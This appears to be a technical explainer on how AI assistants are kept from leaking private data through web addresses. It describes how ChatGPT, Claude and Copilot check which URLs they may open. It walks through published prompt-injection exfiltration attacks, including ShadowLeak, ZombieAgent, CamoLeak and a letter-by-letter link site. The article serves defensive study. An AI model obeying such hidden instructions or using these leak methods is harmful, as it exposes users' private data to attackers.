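Claude can't open an address that appears only in its own output or in the system prompt, which holds the developer's standing instructions to the model. A developer who wants Claude to open an address from the system prompt has to repeat it in a user message. Anthropic also excludes addresses that appear only in the results of most tools that run on its own servers, including its code execution tool and its connector for MCP services. If Claude tries to open an address found only in these excluded sources, it receives the error `url_not_in_prior_context`.

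The tool also rejects any address longer than 250 characters. This limits how much data one request could carry, but it wouldn't block the clinic address in the first example, which has only 57. The tool also rejects an address that seems to contain a password or key, unless that credential appeared in the system prompt or in the text of a user message.

Developers can add a list of permitted domains or a list of forbidden ones, but not both. The early 2026 edition of Anthropic's *web fetch tool* explains that an entry covers the domain's subdomains and can be narrowed to a path, and warns about look-alike names, such as `amazon.com` spelled with a Cyrillic first letter.

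A domain list and URL anchoring each block some requests that the other allows. If a developer permits `docs.google.com`, the anchoring rule still stops Claude from opening a link it composed to submit private data to a Google Form. If an attacker's page turns up in a search, the domain list stops Claude from opening it.

The mid-2026 edition of Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* warned of "residual risk" despite the rule, and told developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. Developers worried about exfiltration could also disable the tool, restrict its domains or cap the number of fetches, which was unlimited by default. The warning mentioned only addresses from the user and from earlier searches and fetches. A fuller list further down the page added client-side tool results, so a developer who read only the warning would have thought the rule stricter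 than it was.

### Differences between Claude products

The consumer Claude app could open web pages before the developer tool existed. Willison (2025) noticed on 2 May that it would fetch a link pasted into a chat. *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* (Willison, 2026) includes a test from that September, which used a page that displays the requests it receives. The app refused to open addresses that Claude had constructed, and Willison presumed that it looked for an exact match with the user's text.

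At first, the app and the developer tool both accepted links found inside pages that Claude had already fetched. According to Willison (2026), Anthropic stopped the app from accepting these links after a researcher used them to extract a user's personal details, a leak made public in July 2026. The developer tool still accepted them in November.

Anthropic also runs Managed Agents, a service that hosts long-running agents for developers. The service opened in April 2026 but didn't adopt the anchoring rule until 7 October, according to Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* (2026). For the first six months, the service's web fetch tool apparently could open addresses that Claude had composed. The new rule is stricter than the developer tool's in one respect, because it doesn't accept addresses from the output of tools that run commands or read files.

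| Where the address appeared | Developer tool | Managed Agents | Claude app |
|---|---|---|---|
| User's message | Counts | Counts | Counts |
| Web search result | Counts | Counts | Counts |
| Page fetched earlier | Counts | Counts | Doesn't count since July 2026 |
| Output of other tools | Counts if the tool is client-side | Doesn't count | Doesn't count |
| Claude's own output | Doesn't count | Doesn't count | Doesn't count |

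The developer tool is also the most adjustable. Its `url_sources` setting, absent from the mid-2026 documentation, lets developers switch off any of the three sources or accept results only from named tools. A developer who accepts only user messages and web search results gets roughly the rule the app now uses. Since 20 October 2026, administrators have also been able to turn off web fetch for their whole organisation or set domain lists that apply to all its developers.

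### ChatGPT's first check and its partial matches

In December 2023, well before Anthropic's tool appeared, OpenAI added a partial check to ChatGPT, called `url_safe`, that used a conversation-based rule. In 2024 the security company Imperva worked out much of how the check operated. Imperva's *From ChatBot To SpyBot* reports that, with the check in place, ChatGPT displayed an image or opened a page only if its address had already appeared in the conversation.

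Imperva sent test strings to the part of ChatGPT that decided whether to open an address. The software apparently searched all the text the user had supplied for the requested string, rather than compiling a list of addresses. The string didn't have to be a valid address. This check stopped an attacker from adding private data to the end of a known address, since the longer string would not be in the text. But it accepted any shortened version. If the text contained `https://bistro.example/menu`, then `https://bistro.example/m` passed too.

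One long address therefore provided dozens of permitted ones, each cut off at a different point. Hidden instructions could make ChatGPT reveal a character of a password by loading the address assigned to that character. Requiring an exact match would have prevented this, but Imperva also got data out by supplying a separate address for each character, which an exact match would have allowed.

The check also had exceptions for certain domains. ChatGPT accepted any plain domain without a path, such as `bistro.example`, even if the user had never mentioned it. An attacker could buy a few dozen domains for a dollar or two each and use each one to represent a character. ChatGPT also accepted any subdomain of `google.com` and any address on `openai.com`. Imperva pointed out that an open redirect on one of these domains could have bypassed the check, but Imperva didn't need to find one.

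Custom instructions, a ChatGPT setting that applies to every new conversation, counted as the user's text. OpenAI evidently assumed that only the user would write them. Imperva had earlier found flaws in ChatGPT's website that could let an attacker run a script there and change the instructions. Addresses the attacker added there would then count as the user's own, even after any stolen login had expired.

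Imperva still thought OpenAI was moving in the right direction. Before the check, an attacker could use one image to send out a whole summary of a conversation. Afterwards, the attacker had to collect the data one character at a time, which made it much harder to take large amounts unnoticed.

Anthropic made a similar mistake in Claude Code, which has a separate web tool with a list of trusted domains. *CVE 2026 24052*, an entry in the software security company Sonatype's vulnerability guide, explains that the tool only checked whether a requested domain began with a trusted one. An attacker could register a longer domain with the same beginning, and Claude Code might then contact it without asking the user. This was worse than accepting shortened addresses, because the attacker controlled the server and the model could write anything after the domain. Anthropic fixed the check in version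 1.0.111.

### ShadowLeak and the exact-address rule

OpenAI's check didn't cover every way that ChatGPT could open a page. In February 2025 the company introduced Deep Research, an agent that spends up to half an hour reading websites, and the user's email if it is connected, before writing a report. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes how the security company's researchers used a single email to leak data through the agent. They saw restrictions on the images ChatGPT displayed, but no comparable restrictions on the addresses that Deep Research opened directly from OpenAI's servers.

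The email contained hidden instructions and a URL, supposedly for a staff directory, with blanks for an employee's name and home address. When the user asked Deep Research to go through the day's email, the agent found those details in another message, added them to the URL and opened it. Nothing appeared on the user's screen, and an employer's network monitoring could not detect the request because it came from OpenAI.

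The attack didn't work at first. The agent recognised direct requests as malicious, and sometimes searched for information about the address instead of opening it. Radware noticed that these refusals were inconsistent and kept revising the email. The final version had the agent encode the details first, so the software that sent the request received only a meaningless string. That version succeeded every time in repeated tests.

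OpenAI's restrictions had depended on the model or the software detecting something suspicious. An anchoring rule would have blocked the request simply because the completed address wasn't the one in the email.

Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it in early August without telling Radware, and acknowledged it on 3 September. Radware's later report, *ZombieAgent*, describes the rule OpenAI adopted against such attacks. ChatGPT would open an address only exactly as it had received it, and refused to add anything to the address even when told to. Radware doesn't say whether this rule was the August fix. It also doesn't say whether software enforced the rule or the model had learned to follow it. The rule would be deterministic only if software enforced it.

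OpenAI also stopped ChatGPT from opening an attacker's addresses if they came from Memory, the feature that stores facts about the user between conversations. Imperva had found much the same danger in custom instructions, where one successful attack could supply addresses for every later chat.

ChatGPT could no longer fill in a gap in an address, but it could still open any complete address that a stranger had emailed to the user. Radware soon used this to leak data again by having ChatGPT choose among addresses listed in an email.

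### When an attacker writes the approved text

Conversation-based anchoring assumes that addresses in text from approved sources are safe to open. Willison (2025) was at first hopeful about Anthropic's tool, because accepting addresses only from the user would have been a strong defence. He then realised that "user messages" often contain text written by other people.

A program that summarises emails might combine the user's request and the email into one block of text and send it to Claude as a user message. Every link in the email then counts as one the user provided. The same happens when someone pastes in text from a website, as in Samoilenko's copy-and-paste attack on ChatGPT.

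The rule allows an address based on where it appears in the conversation, which is only a rough guide to who wrote it. Anthropic's tool excludes addresses in the system prompt, which the developer usually writes, but accepts those in fetched pages, which anyone may have written. Software can reliably check where an address appears, but it often can't tell which sentences of a user message the user typed.

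Text from strangers does limited damage if they wrote it in advance. It can add the attacker's addresses to the list of addresses the assistant may open, and if the assistant opens one, the attacker learns that someone's assistant has read the text. To learn more, the attacker has to get the model to choose which of several addresses to open.

Tools that repeat the model's own words are a more serious problem. Suppose a developer gives Claude a client-side tool that runs short programs and returns whatever they print. Claude writes a program that prints an address containing the clinic appointment. Because the address then appears in a client-side tool result, web fetch will open it. An address that Claude composed has leaked the whole appointment in one request.

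Anthropic describes this problem in its documentation, with a code-running tool as the example. The developer can exclude that tool with `url_sources`, but Anthropic warns that other tools may also repeat Claude's text, for instance in an error message that quotes a faulty command. By default, all client-side tools count as sources of addresses, probably because they often supply ones that users need, such as results from a company's document search. The check for credentials would catch some passwords and keys leaked this way, but "clinic-tuesday-0900" doesn't look like either.

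Developers who handle private data should therefore switch off client-side tool results, or accept them only from tools that can't repeat the model's input. They should also keep outside text out of user messages. If the email program delivered each message as a tool result, the developer could exclude that tool and still let Claude open links the user typed.

Each source a developer removes also makes the assistant less useful. If the assistant can't open links from fetched pages, it can't follow a table of contents or go on to the second page of an article unless a search also returns that page. Even with every source allowed, Claude can't open a well-known newspaper's home page from memory. It has to search for the page or ask the user for the link first, although the address is public and contains nothing private. OpenAI later dealt with this by checking whether its crawler had already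 recorded the address.

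## Opening only addresses found in a public index

OpenAI's current rule lets ChatGPT open an address that is already public, even if the address hasn't appeared in the conversation. ChatGPT can therefore open a newspaper's home page from memory. OpenAI calls this form of URL anchoring Safe Url. It explained the rule in a blog post on 28 January 2026 and gave the technical details in a paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*.

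### How an address passes the check

OpenAI builds its index with a crawler, a program that scans public pages and records the addresses it finds. According to OpenAI, the crawler has no access to conversations, accounts or personal data. When ChatGPT is about to open an address automatically, the software looks for it in the index:

1. If the index contains the address, ChatGPT opens the page or displays the image.
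2. If it doesn't, the software treats the address as unverified. It either tells the model to try a different website or shows the user a warning, and nothing loads unless the user decides to open the link.

ChatGPT also seems to keep a narrow version of the conversation rule. As Rehberger understands it, an address the user types into a message counts as safe for the rest of that chat (Embrace The Red, *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*).

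In the restaurant example, the attacker could get `https://pictures.example/dot.png` into the index by linking to it from a public page, but the version ending in `?note=clinic-tuesday-0900` would still be unverified.

The two kinds of anchoring give different results for some ordinary addresses:

| Address | Rule based on the conversation | Rule based on a public index |
|---|---|---|
| A newspaper's home page that the model remembers | Refused | Opens |
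| A public page with the user's appointment added to its address | Refused | Unverified |
| An article published a few minutes ago, linked from a page the assistant has read | Opens if links in fetched pages count | Unverified until the crawler finds it |
| A private link to a shared document, found in an email | Opens if email results count | Unverified |

An index is also harder for an attacker to influence at short notice, because they have to publish an address and wait for the crawler to find it. Under a conversation rule that accepts links from email, an attacker can add an address to the permitted list just by sending a message.

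### What the guarantee depends on

OpenAI makes one specific promise, to prevent the agent from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself". The crawler recorded the address without knowing anything about the user, so the model can't have written the user's data into it. As with conversation-based anchoring, an attacker can still learn something by having the model choose among many permitted addresses, which the paper acknowledges.

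This reasoning holds only if the index is independent of users' conversations. If a user approved an unverified link and the software then added it to the index, the next request for that link would go through without a warning, along with any private data it contained. OpenAI's products do open pages for users, so the company has to keep those addresses separate from the ones its crawler finds. OpenAI makes this distinction in its documentation for website owners. It says that a program called ChatGPT-User visits pages in response to users' questions and isn't used for automatic crawling. It doesn't say there which of its crawlers supplies Safe Url.

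Even a public address can contain private data. *The Silent Spill* (2026), a study of sensitive data in public collections of web addresses, cites an earlier report on security tools that exposed private links through the scanning site urlscan.io. OpenAI therefore says only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain the user's data. If such an address is already in the index, opening it gives an attacker little, since anyone could have found the data there. But the rule needs an independent index, and one built from links that security tools had collected from people's inboxes would not be independent.

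The guarantee also requires an exact match, which is hard to define because many different addresses can lead to the same page. They may differ in capital letters, a final slash, the order of the values in the query or a tag that records where a visitor came from. Software often normalises addresses, converting them to a standard form before comparing them. This reduces false alarms, but an attacker can use any difference that the comparison ignores to send data.

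If the check ignored capitals in the path, the model could write each of the nine letters of `lunch-menu` in `https://bistro.example/lunch-menu` in upper or lower case. That gives 512 versions of the address, enough to tell the attacker's server the hour of an appointment in the next three weeks. Ignoring the query would be far worse, because the model could then add anything to a public address. The developer can avoid both problems by sending the version stored in the index instead of the one the model wrote.

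Text after a `#` sign needs similar care because, when a full browser opens the page, scripts on the page can read that text and send it on. A developer might leave it out of the comparison because browsers don't send it to the server. OpenAI's post refers to an "exact URL" without saying how the software treats any of these variants.

Redirects are the other difficulty, because an indexed address may forward the request to one that the crawler has never seen. As with conversation-based anchoring, this does little harm if OpenAI's server makes the request without logging in anywhere. The risk is greater in a browser where the user is logged in, because a site can then put the user's account name or other personal details into the address it redirects to. Checking every address along the way would catch this, but would also block many harmless redirects to new or personalised pages. The post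 criticises lists of trusted sites for mishandling redirects, but doesn't explain how Safe Url handles them.

OpenAI acknowledges that Safe Url doesn't make a page's contents trustworthy. The restaurant reviews with the hidden paragraph were on a public page, so ChatGPT could open that page and read the instructions.

### From url_safe to the index

OpenAI's first check, the `url_safe` feature of December 2023, ran partly in the user's browser. Before ChatGPT's web page displayed an image, it sent the image's address to an OpenAI server, which labeled it safe or unsafe. Embrace The Red reports that Rehberger could see these labels but not the reasons for them. Rehberger tried 36 image addresses on one website, one for each letter and digit, and nine passed, with no obvious difference from the rest. Rehberger speculated at the time that ChatGPT might be looking addresses up in Bing's index.

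Because the check ran in the web page, OpenAI had to build it separately into every other version of ChatGPT. The iPhone app didn't have it at first, and Rehberger later found it missing from the Mac app too. He suggested moving the check to OpenAI's servers, where one version could protect every app.

According to Tenable's *HackedGPT*, the verdicts depended partly on whether OpenAI trusted the domain, whether the address had a subdomain or a query and whether OpenAI trusted those, and what had appeared in the conversation. The check therefore combined URL anchoring with a list of trusted domains, and researchers repeatedly got around it through that list.

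Rehberger told OpenAI in October 2024 about two trusted domains, `windows.net` and `apache.org`, where outsiders could read the server's logs. Microsoft uses `windows.net` for cloud storage, and anyone can open a storage account there and see which requests reach it. OpenAI had evidently assumed only Microsoft would see data sent to that domain. Embrace The Red's *AI Domination* describes a talk at that year's Black Hat Europe conference in which Rehberger also presented ways around `url_safe`.

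The storage route still worked in 2025, and it could expose more by then because ChatGPT had begun to give the model information about the user's recent conversations along with its standing instructions. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* shows how a web page or a PDF could make ChatGPT put this information into the address of an image on Rehberger's storage account. Rehberger recommended that OpenAI publish its list of trusted domains and let business customers change it.

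Tenable found another weak entry and reported it on 10 December 2024. ChatGPT treated every address on `bing.com` as safe, but Bing gives each website in its search results a fixed tracking link on `bing.com` that redirects to the site. An attacker whose site appeared in Bing could copy its tracking link, and ChatGPT would accept it. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* calls this "an open redirect as a service". Imperva had warned about this kind of weakness.

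Adding text to these tracking links breaks them, so Tenable leaked data by giving each letter its own page and link. The researchers also had to get past a barrier OpenAI had put between web pages and the user's data. ChatGPT handed pages to a separate model, which Tenable calls SearchGPT, that couldn't see the user's memories or earlier messages. SearchGPT's summary still became part of the conversation, and ChatGPT read it when the user sent the next message, so hostile text could do more harm than OpenAI's designers had assumed. A comment on a blog could make SearchGPT end its summary with new instructions, which ChatGPT then followed as if they were its own earlier words. Another version of the attack put the instructions in ChatGPT's memory, so every later answer leaked data.

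The repairs took a long time. Tenable's advisory records six requests for updates between December 2024 and March 2025, and the flaw was still open when Tenable published the advisory. On 11 July 2025, OpenAI told Tenable that it had improved the check, according to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025). Rehberger noticed that the browser no longer showed the verdicts. Further changes, which he dates to about August 2025, stopped the attacks shown at Black Hat and in a later series of posts.

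Tenable reported in November 2025 that several of its demonstrations still worked with GPT-5, which OpenAI had introduced that summer. Two of them relied on the Bing links. One showed the user a malicious link, and the other leaked data after ChatGPT read instructions in a blog comment. Tenable doesn't say when it ran these tests, so it may have run them before OpenAI finished the August changes.

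It is also unclear when OpenAI began using the index. Rehberger treats the paper as explaining the recent changes, which suggests that at least part of the system was running by August. The rule for links in email seems to have come later. *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, a January 2026 news article, reports that OpenAI responded to Radware's ZombieAgent attack by refusing to open links from emails unless they appeared in a well-known public index or the user had supplied them.

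### Trusted sites compared with a public index

OpenAI gives two reasons for not relying on a list of trusted sites. The first is that a trusted site may redirect to an untrusted one. Tenable had used Bing redirects this way to attack OpenAI's own product, so OpenAI knew of the problem. But a developer can fix it without an index by checking each redirect, as browsers do when they enforce a content security policy.

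Rehberger's attack using a storage account is a better argument for the index. The data went to a trusted domain and stayed there, so checking every redirect would not have stopped it. Opening only indexed addresses would have, because no crawler had seen an address containing that user's chat history.

OpenAI's second reason is that people visit far more than a few well-known sites. A strict list would often produce warnings about harmless pages, and people who see too many warnings learn to click through them without reading. An index covers many more pages than a list maintained by hand, but it also produces false alarms.

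New pages fail the index check until the crawler has found them, which matters most when someone asks about the day's news. Private pages also fail, including shared documents, parcel tracking pages and a company's internal sites. Caution is reasonable for private pages because the address may be a secret that lets anyone who has it see the page.

Personalised pages are the hardest case. To check whether a restaurant has a free table, an assistant might need to open `https://bistro.example/book?day=tuesday&guests=4`. The user wants the restaurant to have this information, but the address contains details from the conversation, just as a leak would. Software that checks only the index can't tell the two apart. A list of trusted sites that included `bistro.example` could allow the request, but it would also let the assistant send the restaurant any other data.

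Some websites also keep crawlers out, by listing pages to avoid in a file called `robots.txt` or by using a service that blocks automated visitors. OpenAI's advice to advertisers says that its crawlers obey `robots.txt` and that such services can block them. ChatGPT may still have the address of a page that its crawler can't read, because other sites link to it. OpenAI's documentation for website owners says that sites that refuse its search crawler can still appear in ChatGPT as navigational links. The documentation doesn't say whether Safe Url treats these addresses as public.

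The number of sites that refuse may be small. The trade publication Search Engine Journal reports that disallow rates across Europe are in the single digits for most of the newest AI agents. ChatGPT-User is an exception, but it fetches pages for users and isn't the crawler. These rates cover only `robots.txt` rules, so they leave out sites that block crawlers by other means.

OpenAI's search index extends well beyond the publishers OpenAI pays. In July 2026 the search consultancy Resoneo examined 1,249 ChatGPT answers, which included results from hundreds of outlets that had no content deal with OpenAI. According to Search Engine Journal, OpenAI's own index supplied most of the search results that Resoneo collected from free accounts. Rehberger says OpenAI also uses its web index to validate addresses. But Resoneo could study only pages the index had returned, so its figures don't show how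 many pages are missing from the index.

OpenAI makes false alarms less disruptive by letting the assistant try another site. If a new article about a football match isn't in the index, an older report of the same match may be enough, and the user never sees a warning. This doesn't work for a booking or a shared document, which has no substitute. OpenAI's post gives no figures for how often addresses fail the check or how often users see a warning, so outsiders can't tell how much Safe Url reduces either compared with a generous list of trusted sites.

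The index prevents leaks better because it doesn't depend on knowing what strangers can do on each domain, but it is much more expensive. OpenAI and Google already crawl the web for their search products. A small company would have to buy access to an index, or use a public collection and find out where its addresses came from.

### Products with and without the check

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), published six weeks after the first post, explains where Safe Url fits among the company's other defences. It compares an AI agent to a customer service worker who can give refunds. Some customers will lie, and the worker will sometimes believe them, so the employer limits how much any one worker can refund. OpenAI is sceptical of filters that try to recognise malicious text, because spotting a well-written injection is as hard as spotting a lie, often without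 the necessary context.

The post also lists the products covered:

| Product | Protection |
|---|---|
| ChatGPT | Safe Url |
| Atlas, OpenAI's web browser | Safe Url, for navigations and bookmarks |
| Deep Research | Safe Url, for searches and navigations |
| Canvas and apps inside ChatGPT | A sandbox that detects unexpected communications and asks the user for consent |

Searches are presumably on the list because a query can also carry private text to another company. In Deep Research, the check now covers the kind of request that ShadowLeak used.

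According to OpenAI, most attacks on ChatGPT that it knows of fail earlier, because the model refuses to follow the instructions. Outside testers can't easily tell which of the two defences stopped an attack. *The Framing Gap* reports that ChatGPT leaked nothing in 48 valid trials, while the model behind OpenAI's programming interface leaked in up to 100% of trials. The researchers couldn't see inside the product and don't say what made the difference. With only 48 trials, the result is also compatible with a true leak rate of up to about 6%.

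Rehberger considers Safe Url a significant improvement that makes attacks more complex but does not solve the problem, and welcomes OpenAI's decision to publish the details. Rehberger is also concerned that some of OpenAI's many developers may not know the check exists when they build a feature that loads addresses.

This had already happened on the OpenAI Platform, where outside developers build and test products with OpenAI's models. Its log viewer shows what a model wrote. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes a test with an imitation banking tool that checked customers' identities. Hidden instructions made the model write an image address containing a customer's passport and financial details. The tool blocked the answer. But when a developer opened the log to see what had gone wrong, the viewer displayed the image, which made the developer's browser send the data to the attacker.

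The tool's designers assumed that an answer they blocked could do no further harm. A sanitiser or a content security policy in the tool would not have helped either, PromptArmor points out, because neither affects OpenAI's log viewer. PromptArmor found the same fault in OpenAI's previews for testing chats, assistants and agents, and in a sample app that OpenAI gives developers to build on.

PromptArmor reported this on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that handles such reports for OpenAI. The report was closed on 4 December as "Not applicable", and PromptArmor later published its findings. OpenAI said it hadn't seen the report before the findings were published. It confirmed the flaw and reopened the case on 22 January 2026, six days before it published its post about Safe Url.

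A similar gap in ChatGPT's previews of HTML pages, since patched, let a chat's contents leak even in the product's most restrictive mode, according to The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026).

A company can combine the index with a content security policy to guard against developers forgetting to check an image's address. If every page that displays a model's output allows images only from one company server, and that server checks the index before fetching anything, an image whose check was forgotten will fail to load rather than leak data.

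## Leaking data by choosing among permitted addresses

URL anchoring stops an assistant from writing private data into an address, whether the software checks addresses against the conversation or against a public index. But the assistant still chooses which permitted address to open, and that choice can reveal private data to an attacker. Suppose the review page in the restaurant example lists five lunch menus on the attacker's server, one for each weekday. The hidden paragraph contains an instruction to open the menu for the day of the user's next appointment. The model opens `https://bistro.example/tuesday`. The address contains no private data, because the attacker wrote it before the model read the mailbox, but the request shows the attacker that the appointment is on a Tuesday.

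### How much the choices can reveal

One bit of information distinguishes between two equally likely possibilities, and each additional bit doubles that number. If the attacker offers N addresses, one fetch can identify one of N possibilities, which is log₂ N bits. A series of k fetches can form Nᵏ different sequences, so it can carry at most k × log₂ N bits.

A six-digit login code has 1,000,000 possible values, or about 19.9 bits. To leak it, the attacker needs enough fetches for Nᵏ to reach a million:

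- With 10 addresses, one for each digit, six fetches give exactly 10⁶ = 1,000,000 sequences.
- With 36 addresses, three fetches give only 36³ = 46,656 sequences, but four give 36⁴ = 1,679,616.
- With 1,000 addresses, two fetches are enough, because 1,000² = 1,000,000.

If the software refuses to open the same address twice, a model with 36 addresses has 36 options for the first fetch, 35 for the second, 34 for the third and 33 for the fourth. That makes 36 × 35 × 34 × 33 = 1,413,720 sequences, so four fetches still suffice.

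If the requests also arrive in a jumbled order, the attacker learns only which addresses the model opened. Four addresses can arrive in 24 orders, which the attacker can no longer tell apart, so the 1,413,720 sequences shrink to 58,905 sets. Five fetches give 376,992 sets and six give 1,947,792, so the attacker needs six.

| Addresses | Repeats allowed, order known | No repeats, order known | No repeats, order lost |
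|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 6 fetches | 8 fetches | Impossible, since there are only 1,024 sets |
| 36 | 4 fetches | 4 fetches | 6 fetches |
| 1,000 | 2 fetches | 3 fetches | 3 fetches |

The table assumes that the attacker always waits for the same number of requests. It gives the fewest fetches that could work, but the model also has to carry out the encoding, and turning a number into one of 1.9 million sets of addresses is hard without a program. A simpler method is to supply separate addresses for each position. A six-digit code needs 60 addresses, ten for each position. The model opens one from each group, so it never repeats an address, and the attacker can read the code in whatever order the requests arrive.

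### Age brackets and postal codes in ChatGPT

*Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (Schwartzman, 2024) demonstrates this weakness in ChatGPT, which at the time opened only addresses that appeared in the user's prompt. OpenAI had assumed that opening such an address couldn't reveal anything new to its owner. Schwartzman hid instructions in a long piece of code that a victim might paste into ChatGPT, along with an address for each ten-year age bracket. ChatGPT opened the one that matched the user's age. The attack could also work on users who had never stated their age, because ChatGPT could infer it from a remark about leaving school or retiring soon. An earlier injection could also instruct ChatGPT to remember the user's age if it ever came up.

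A second version leaked a postal code. It used a separate address for each digit because ChatGPT wouldn't open the same address twice, which Schwartzman attributed to caching (keeping a copy of a page instead of requesting it again). ChatGPT also accepted shortened addresses, as Imperva found too, so the length of each address it opened could represent a digit. The model made mistakes when it worked out the lengths itself, so Schwartzman added a short program to calculate them.

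ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt, so this version could leak only ten characters at a time. An attacker would need many prompts to steal a document this way, but only one to steal a postal code or login code.

Schwartzman reported the problem to OpenAI through Bugcrowd and was told that it was "non applicable". OpenAI's later rule requiring the exact address would not block the age version, but it would block the postal-code version because that version relied on shortened addresses.

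### CamoLeak and GitHub's signed images

Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes an attack, which the security company discovered in June 2025, on GitHub Copilot Chat, the assistant built into the code-sharing site GitHub. The attacker proposed a change to a project and put instructions in a hidden comment in the description. Hidden comments are a GitHub feature that visitors don't see, but Copilot read them. When another user asked Copilot to explain the proposal, it followed the instructions with that user's access rights, including access to private projects.

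GitHub's content security policy allowed images only from GitHub's own hosts. GitHub shows images from elsewhere through Camo, an image proxy that accepts only addresses GitHub has signed. GitHub assumed that this prevented attackers from sending out data, since the model can't sign an address.

However, GitHub signs image addresses for anyone who submits Markdown containing them. Legit Security's researcher obtained a signed address for every letter and symbol in advance and listed them in the hidden comment. Copilot then spelled out private text as a row of images, each a single transparent pixel. As Camo fetched the images, the researcher's server received the text one character at a time.

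Caching would have hidden repeated letters, so the researcher had Copilot add a new random number to each address. The signature evidently didn't cover this number. An exact-match rule would have blocked the altered addresses, but the attacker could have bypassed it by having GitHub sign several addresses for each letter.

The attack leaked the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project. In another test, Copilot searched the victim's code for Amazon cloud keys and sent out what it found. By 14 August 2025, GitHub had fixed the problem by disabling all images in Copilot Chat. The fix works no matter what an attacker can get GitHub to sign, but it also prevents Copilot from showing diagrams or screenshots in its answers.

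### ZombieAgent and the email full of addresses

OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from adding anything to an address, assuming that an unaltered address couldn't carry the user's data. Radware then switched from one adjustable address to a list of fixed ones. Its ZombieAgent attack used an email that listed an address for each letter and digit and one for the space. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something with Gmail, ChatGPT read the email, found the data specified in it and opened the address for each character in turn. OpenAI's servers sent these requests before the user saw an answer.

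To keep the characters in order, Radware added numbered addresses for each position. A message of 20 letters and digits then needs 36 × 20 = 720 addresses. An email containing that many addresses would look strange, but the attack works even if the recipient never opens it.

The attack could take data from connected services such as Outlook, Google Drive and GitHub, as well as from chat history and memories. Radware also made it persistent. A file that the user shared with ChatGPT planted a rule in its memory to read the attacker's email before every answer. ChatGPT couldn't use its memory after using a connected service in the same chat, but it could still use a connected service after using its memory. OpenAI had also blocked addresses that came from memory, but these addresses came from the email, so the block didn't apply to them.

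In another variant, ChatGPT leaked contacts' addresses from the inbox, and the attacker's server sent each of them the same email.

Radware reported the attack on 26 September 2025 and three days later sent OpenAI an improved version that worked every time. OpenAI fixed the vulnerability on 16 December. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, OpenAI responded by checking links from emails against a public index.

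An attacker can still try to leak data through addresses that are in the index. Embrace The Red points out that any fairly large blog probably has 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit. An attacker with thousands of pages could assign a whole word to each. By the calculation above, a site with 1,000 indexed pages could receive a six-digit code in two fetches.

### How a website gave Claude a keyboard

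In the Claude app, an attacker could generate addresses during the attack instead of listing them in advance. *The Memory Heist* (Paul, 2026) describes how the app could open links on pages it had already fetched. Paul built a website where each page linked to 27 others, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. When Claude followed a link, the server generated a new page with 27 longer addresses, each containing the characters chosen so far plus one more. Claude could spell out a name by moving from page to page.

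Anchoring works only if nobody can add useful addresses after the model has read private data. In this attack, the server added 27 new addresses after every choice, and each one contained what the attacker had already learned. Anthropic had assumed that a link on a fetched page was as safe as one the user supplied. Caching and a ban on repeat visits would have made no difference, because every address was new. The order of the requests didn't matter, because the last address contained the whole name.

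Claude refused cruder attempts, so Paul disguised the site as a coffee shop behind a security check. The check claimed that AI assistants had to spell out their user's name. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* notes that the server showed the check only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, while people saw a normal website. Claude has a summary of past conversations in every chat and a tool for searching the originals, and it gave away Paul's full name, employer and home town. According to dyb's *The Read-Only Lie*, Claude inferred the home town, which Paul had never told it, from the name of a school hackathon.

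The blogger dyb estimates that the attack took about 30 fetches. Each choice among 27 links carries 4.75 bits, so 30 fetches carry about 143 bits. This is less data than a single image address can hold, but it includes the answer to a common security question.

Willison reports that Anthropic told Paul it already knew of the problem, and that it paid no reward. Anthropic then stopped the app from opening links found in fetched pages. Products built on Anthropic's web fetch tool may still have this weakness unless their developers have switched off such links.

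### Choices that are part of the task

In all of these attacks, hidden text told the assistant to reveal something. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack without such an instruction. The attacker's website only offers reference pages on different topics and records which one the assistant opens. In the paper's example, a user asks why influenza can be deadlier than COVID-19 in children. The assistant picks "Biological Mechanisms" over "Clinical Outcomes", and on the next page it picks "Immune Response". The attacker can infer much of the question from these choices.

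The tests covered four agents with three models each. On a set of 500 questions, the site recovered the concepts in each question with an average score of 0.89, where 1 means finding every concept and guessing none wrongly. It needed about 6.5 rounds of links per question. Four existing defences, including Microsoft's Spotlighting, lowered the score by at most 0.03. This makes sense because the agents were doing what their users wanted and never sent any private text.

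The set-up favoured the attacker because the researchers inserted their link into 2,600 pages that the agents were known to visit early in their searches. The score also leaves out the 6% of attempts that gave the site nothing to decode. The researchers didn't test URL anchoring. A rule against following links from fetched pages would have blocked the site's follow-up questions, as would a rule allowing only URLs in a public index, provided the index didn't contain the site's newly generated pages.

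Liang and colleagues also measured how reliable such choices are. The attacker identified the right topic 93.8% of the time when there were four distinct topics, but only 50% of the time when there were 16. If the errors are spread evenly, each choice reveals about 1.6 of a possible 2 bits with four topics, and about 1.0 of a possible 4 bits with 16. A longer list of topics can therefore reveal less than a short one. Spelling avoids this problem because each letter matches only one link.

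### Caching and bans on repeat visits

Rehberger has proposed that the software either keep a copy of each page for a few minutes or refuse to open an address twice in one session. In both cases, the attacker's server receives at most one request for each address, so "anna", sent using one address per letter, would arrive as "an".

These measures limit how much data a fixed list of addresses can leak. If the list has 36 addresses, the model can open each one only once, and the attacker can't see the order, a whole session can leak at most 36 bits, one for whether the model opens each address. If the attacker can see the order, the limit is about 140 bits. To raise the limit, the attacker has to supply more addresses, which is easy in an email but harder when addresses must come from a public index.

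Caching is a small inconvenience for users. Most pages don't change within a few minutes, though someone following a football match would get an old score. A ban on repeat visits is a bigger inconvenience, because the assistant couldn't check again whether concert tickets had gone on sale. The two look the same to the attacker, so caching is the better choice.

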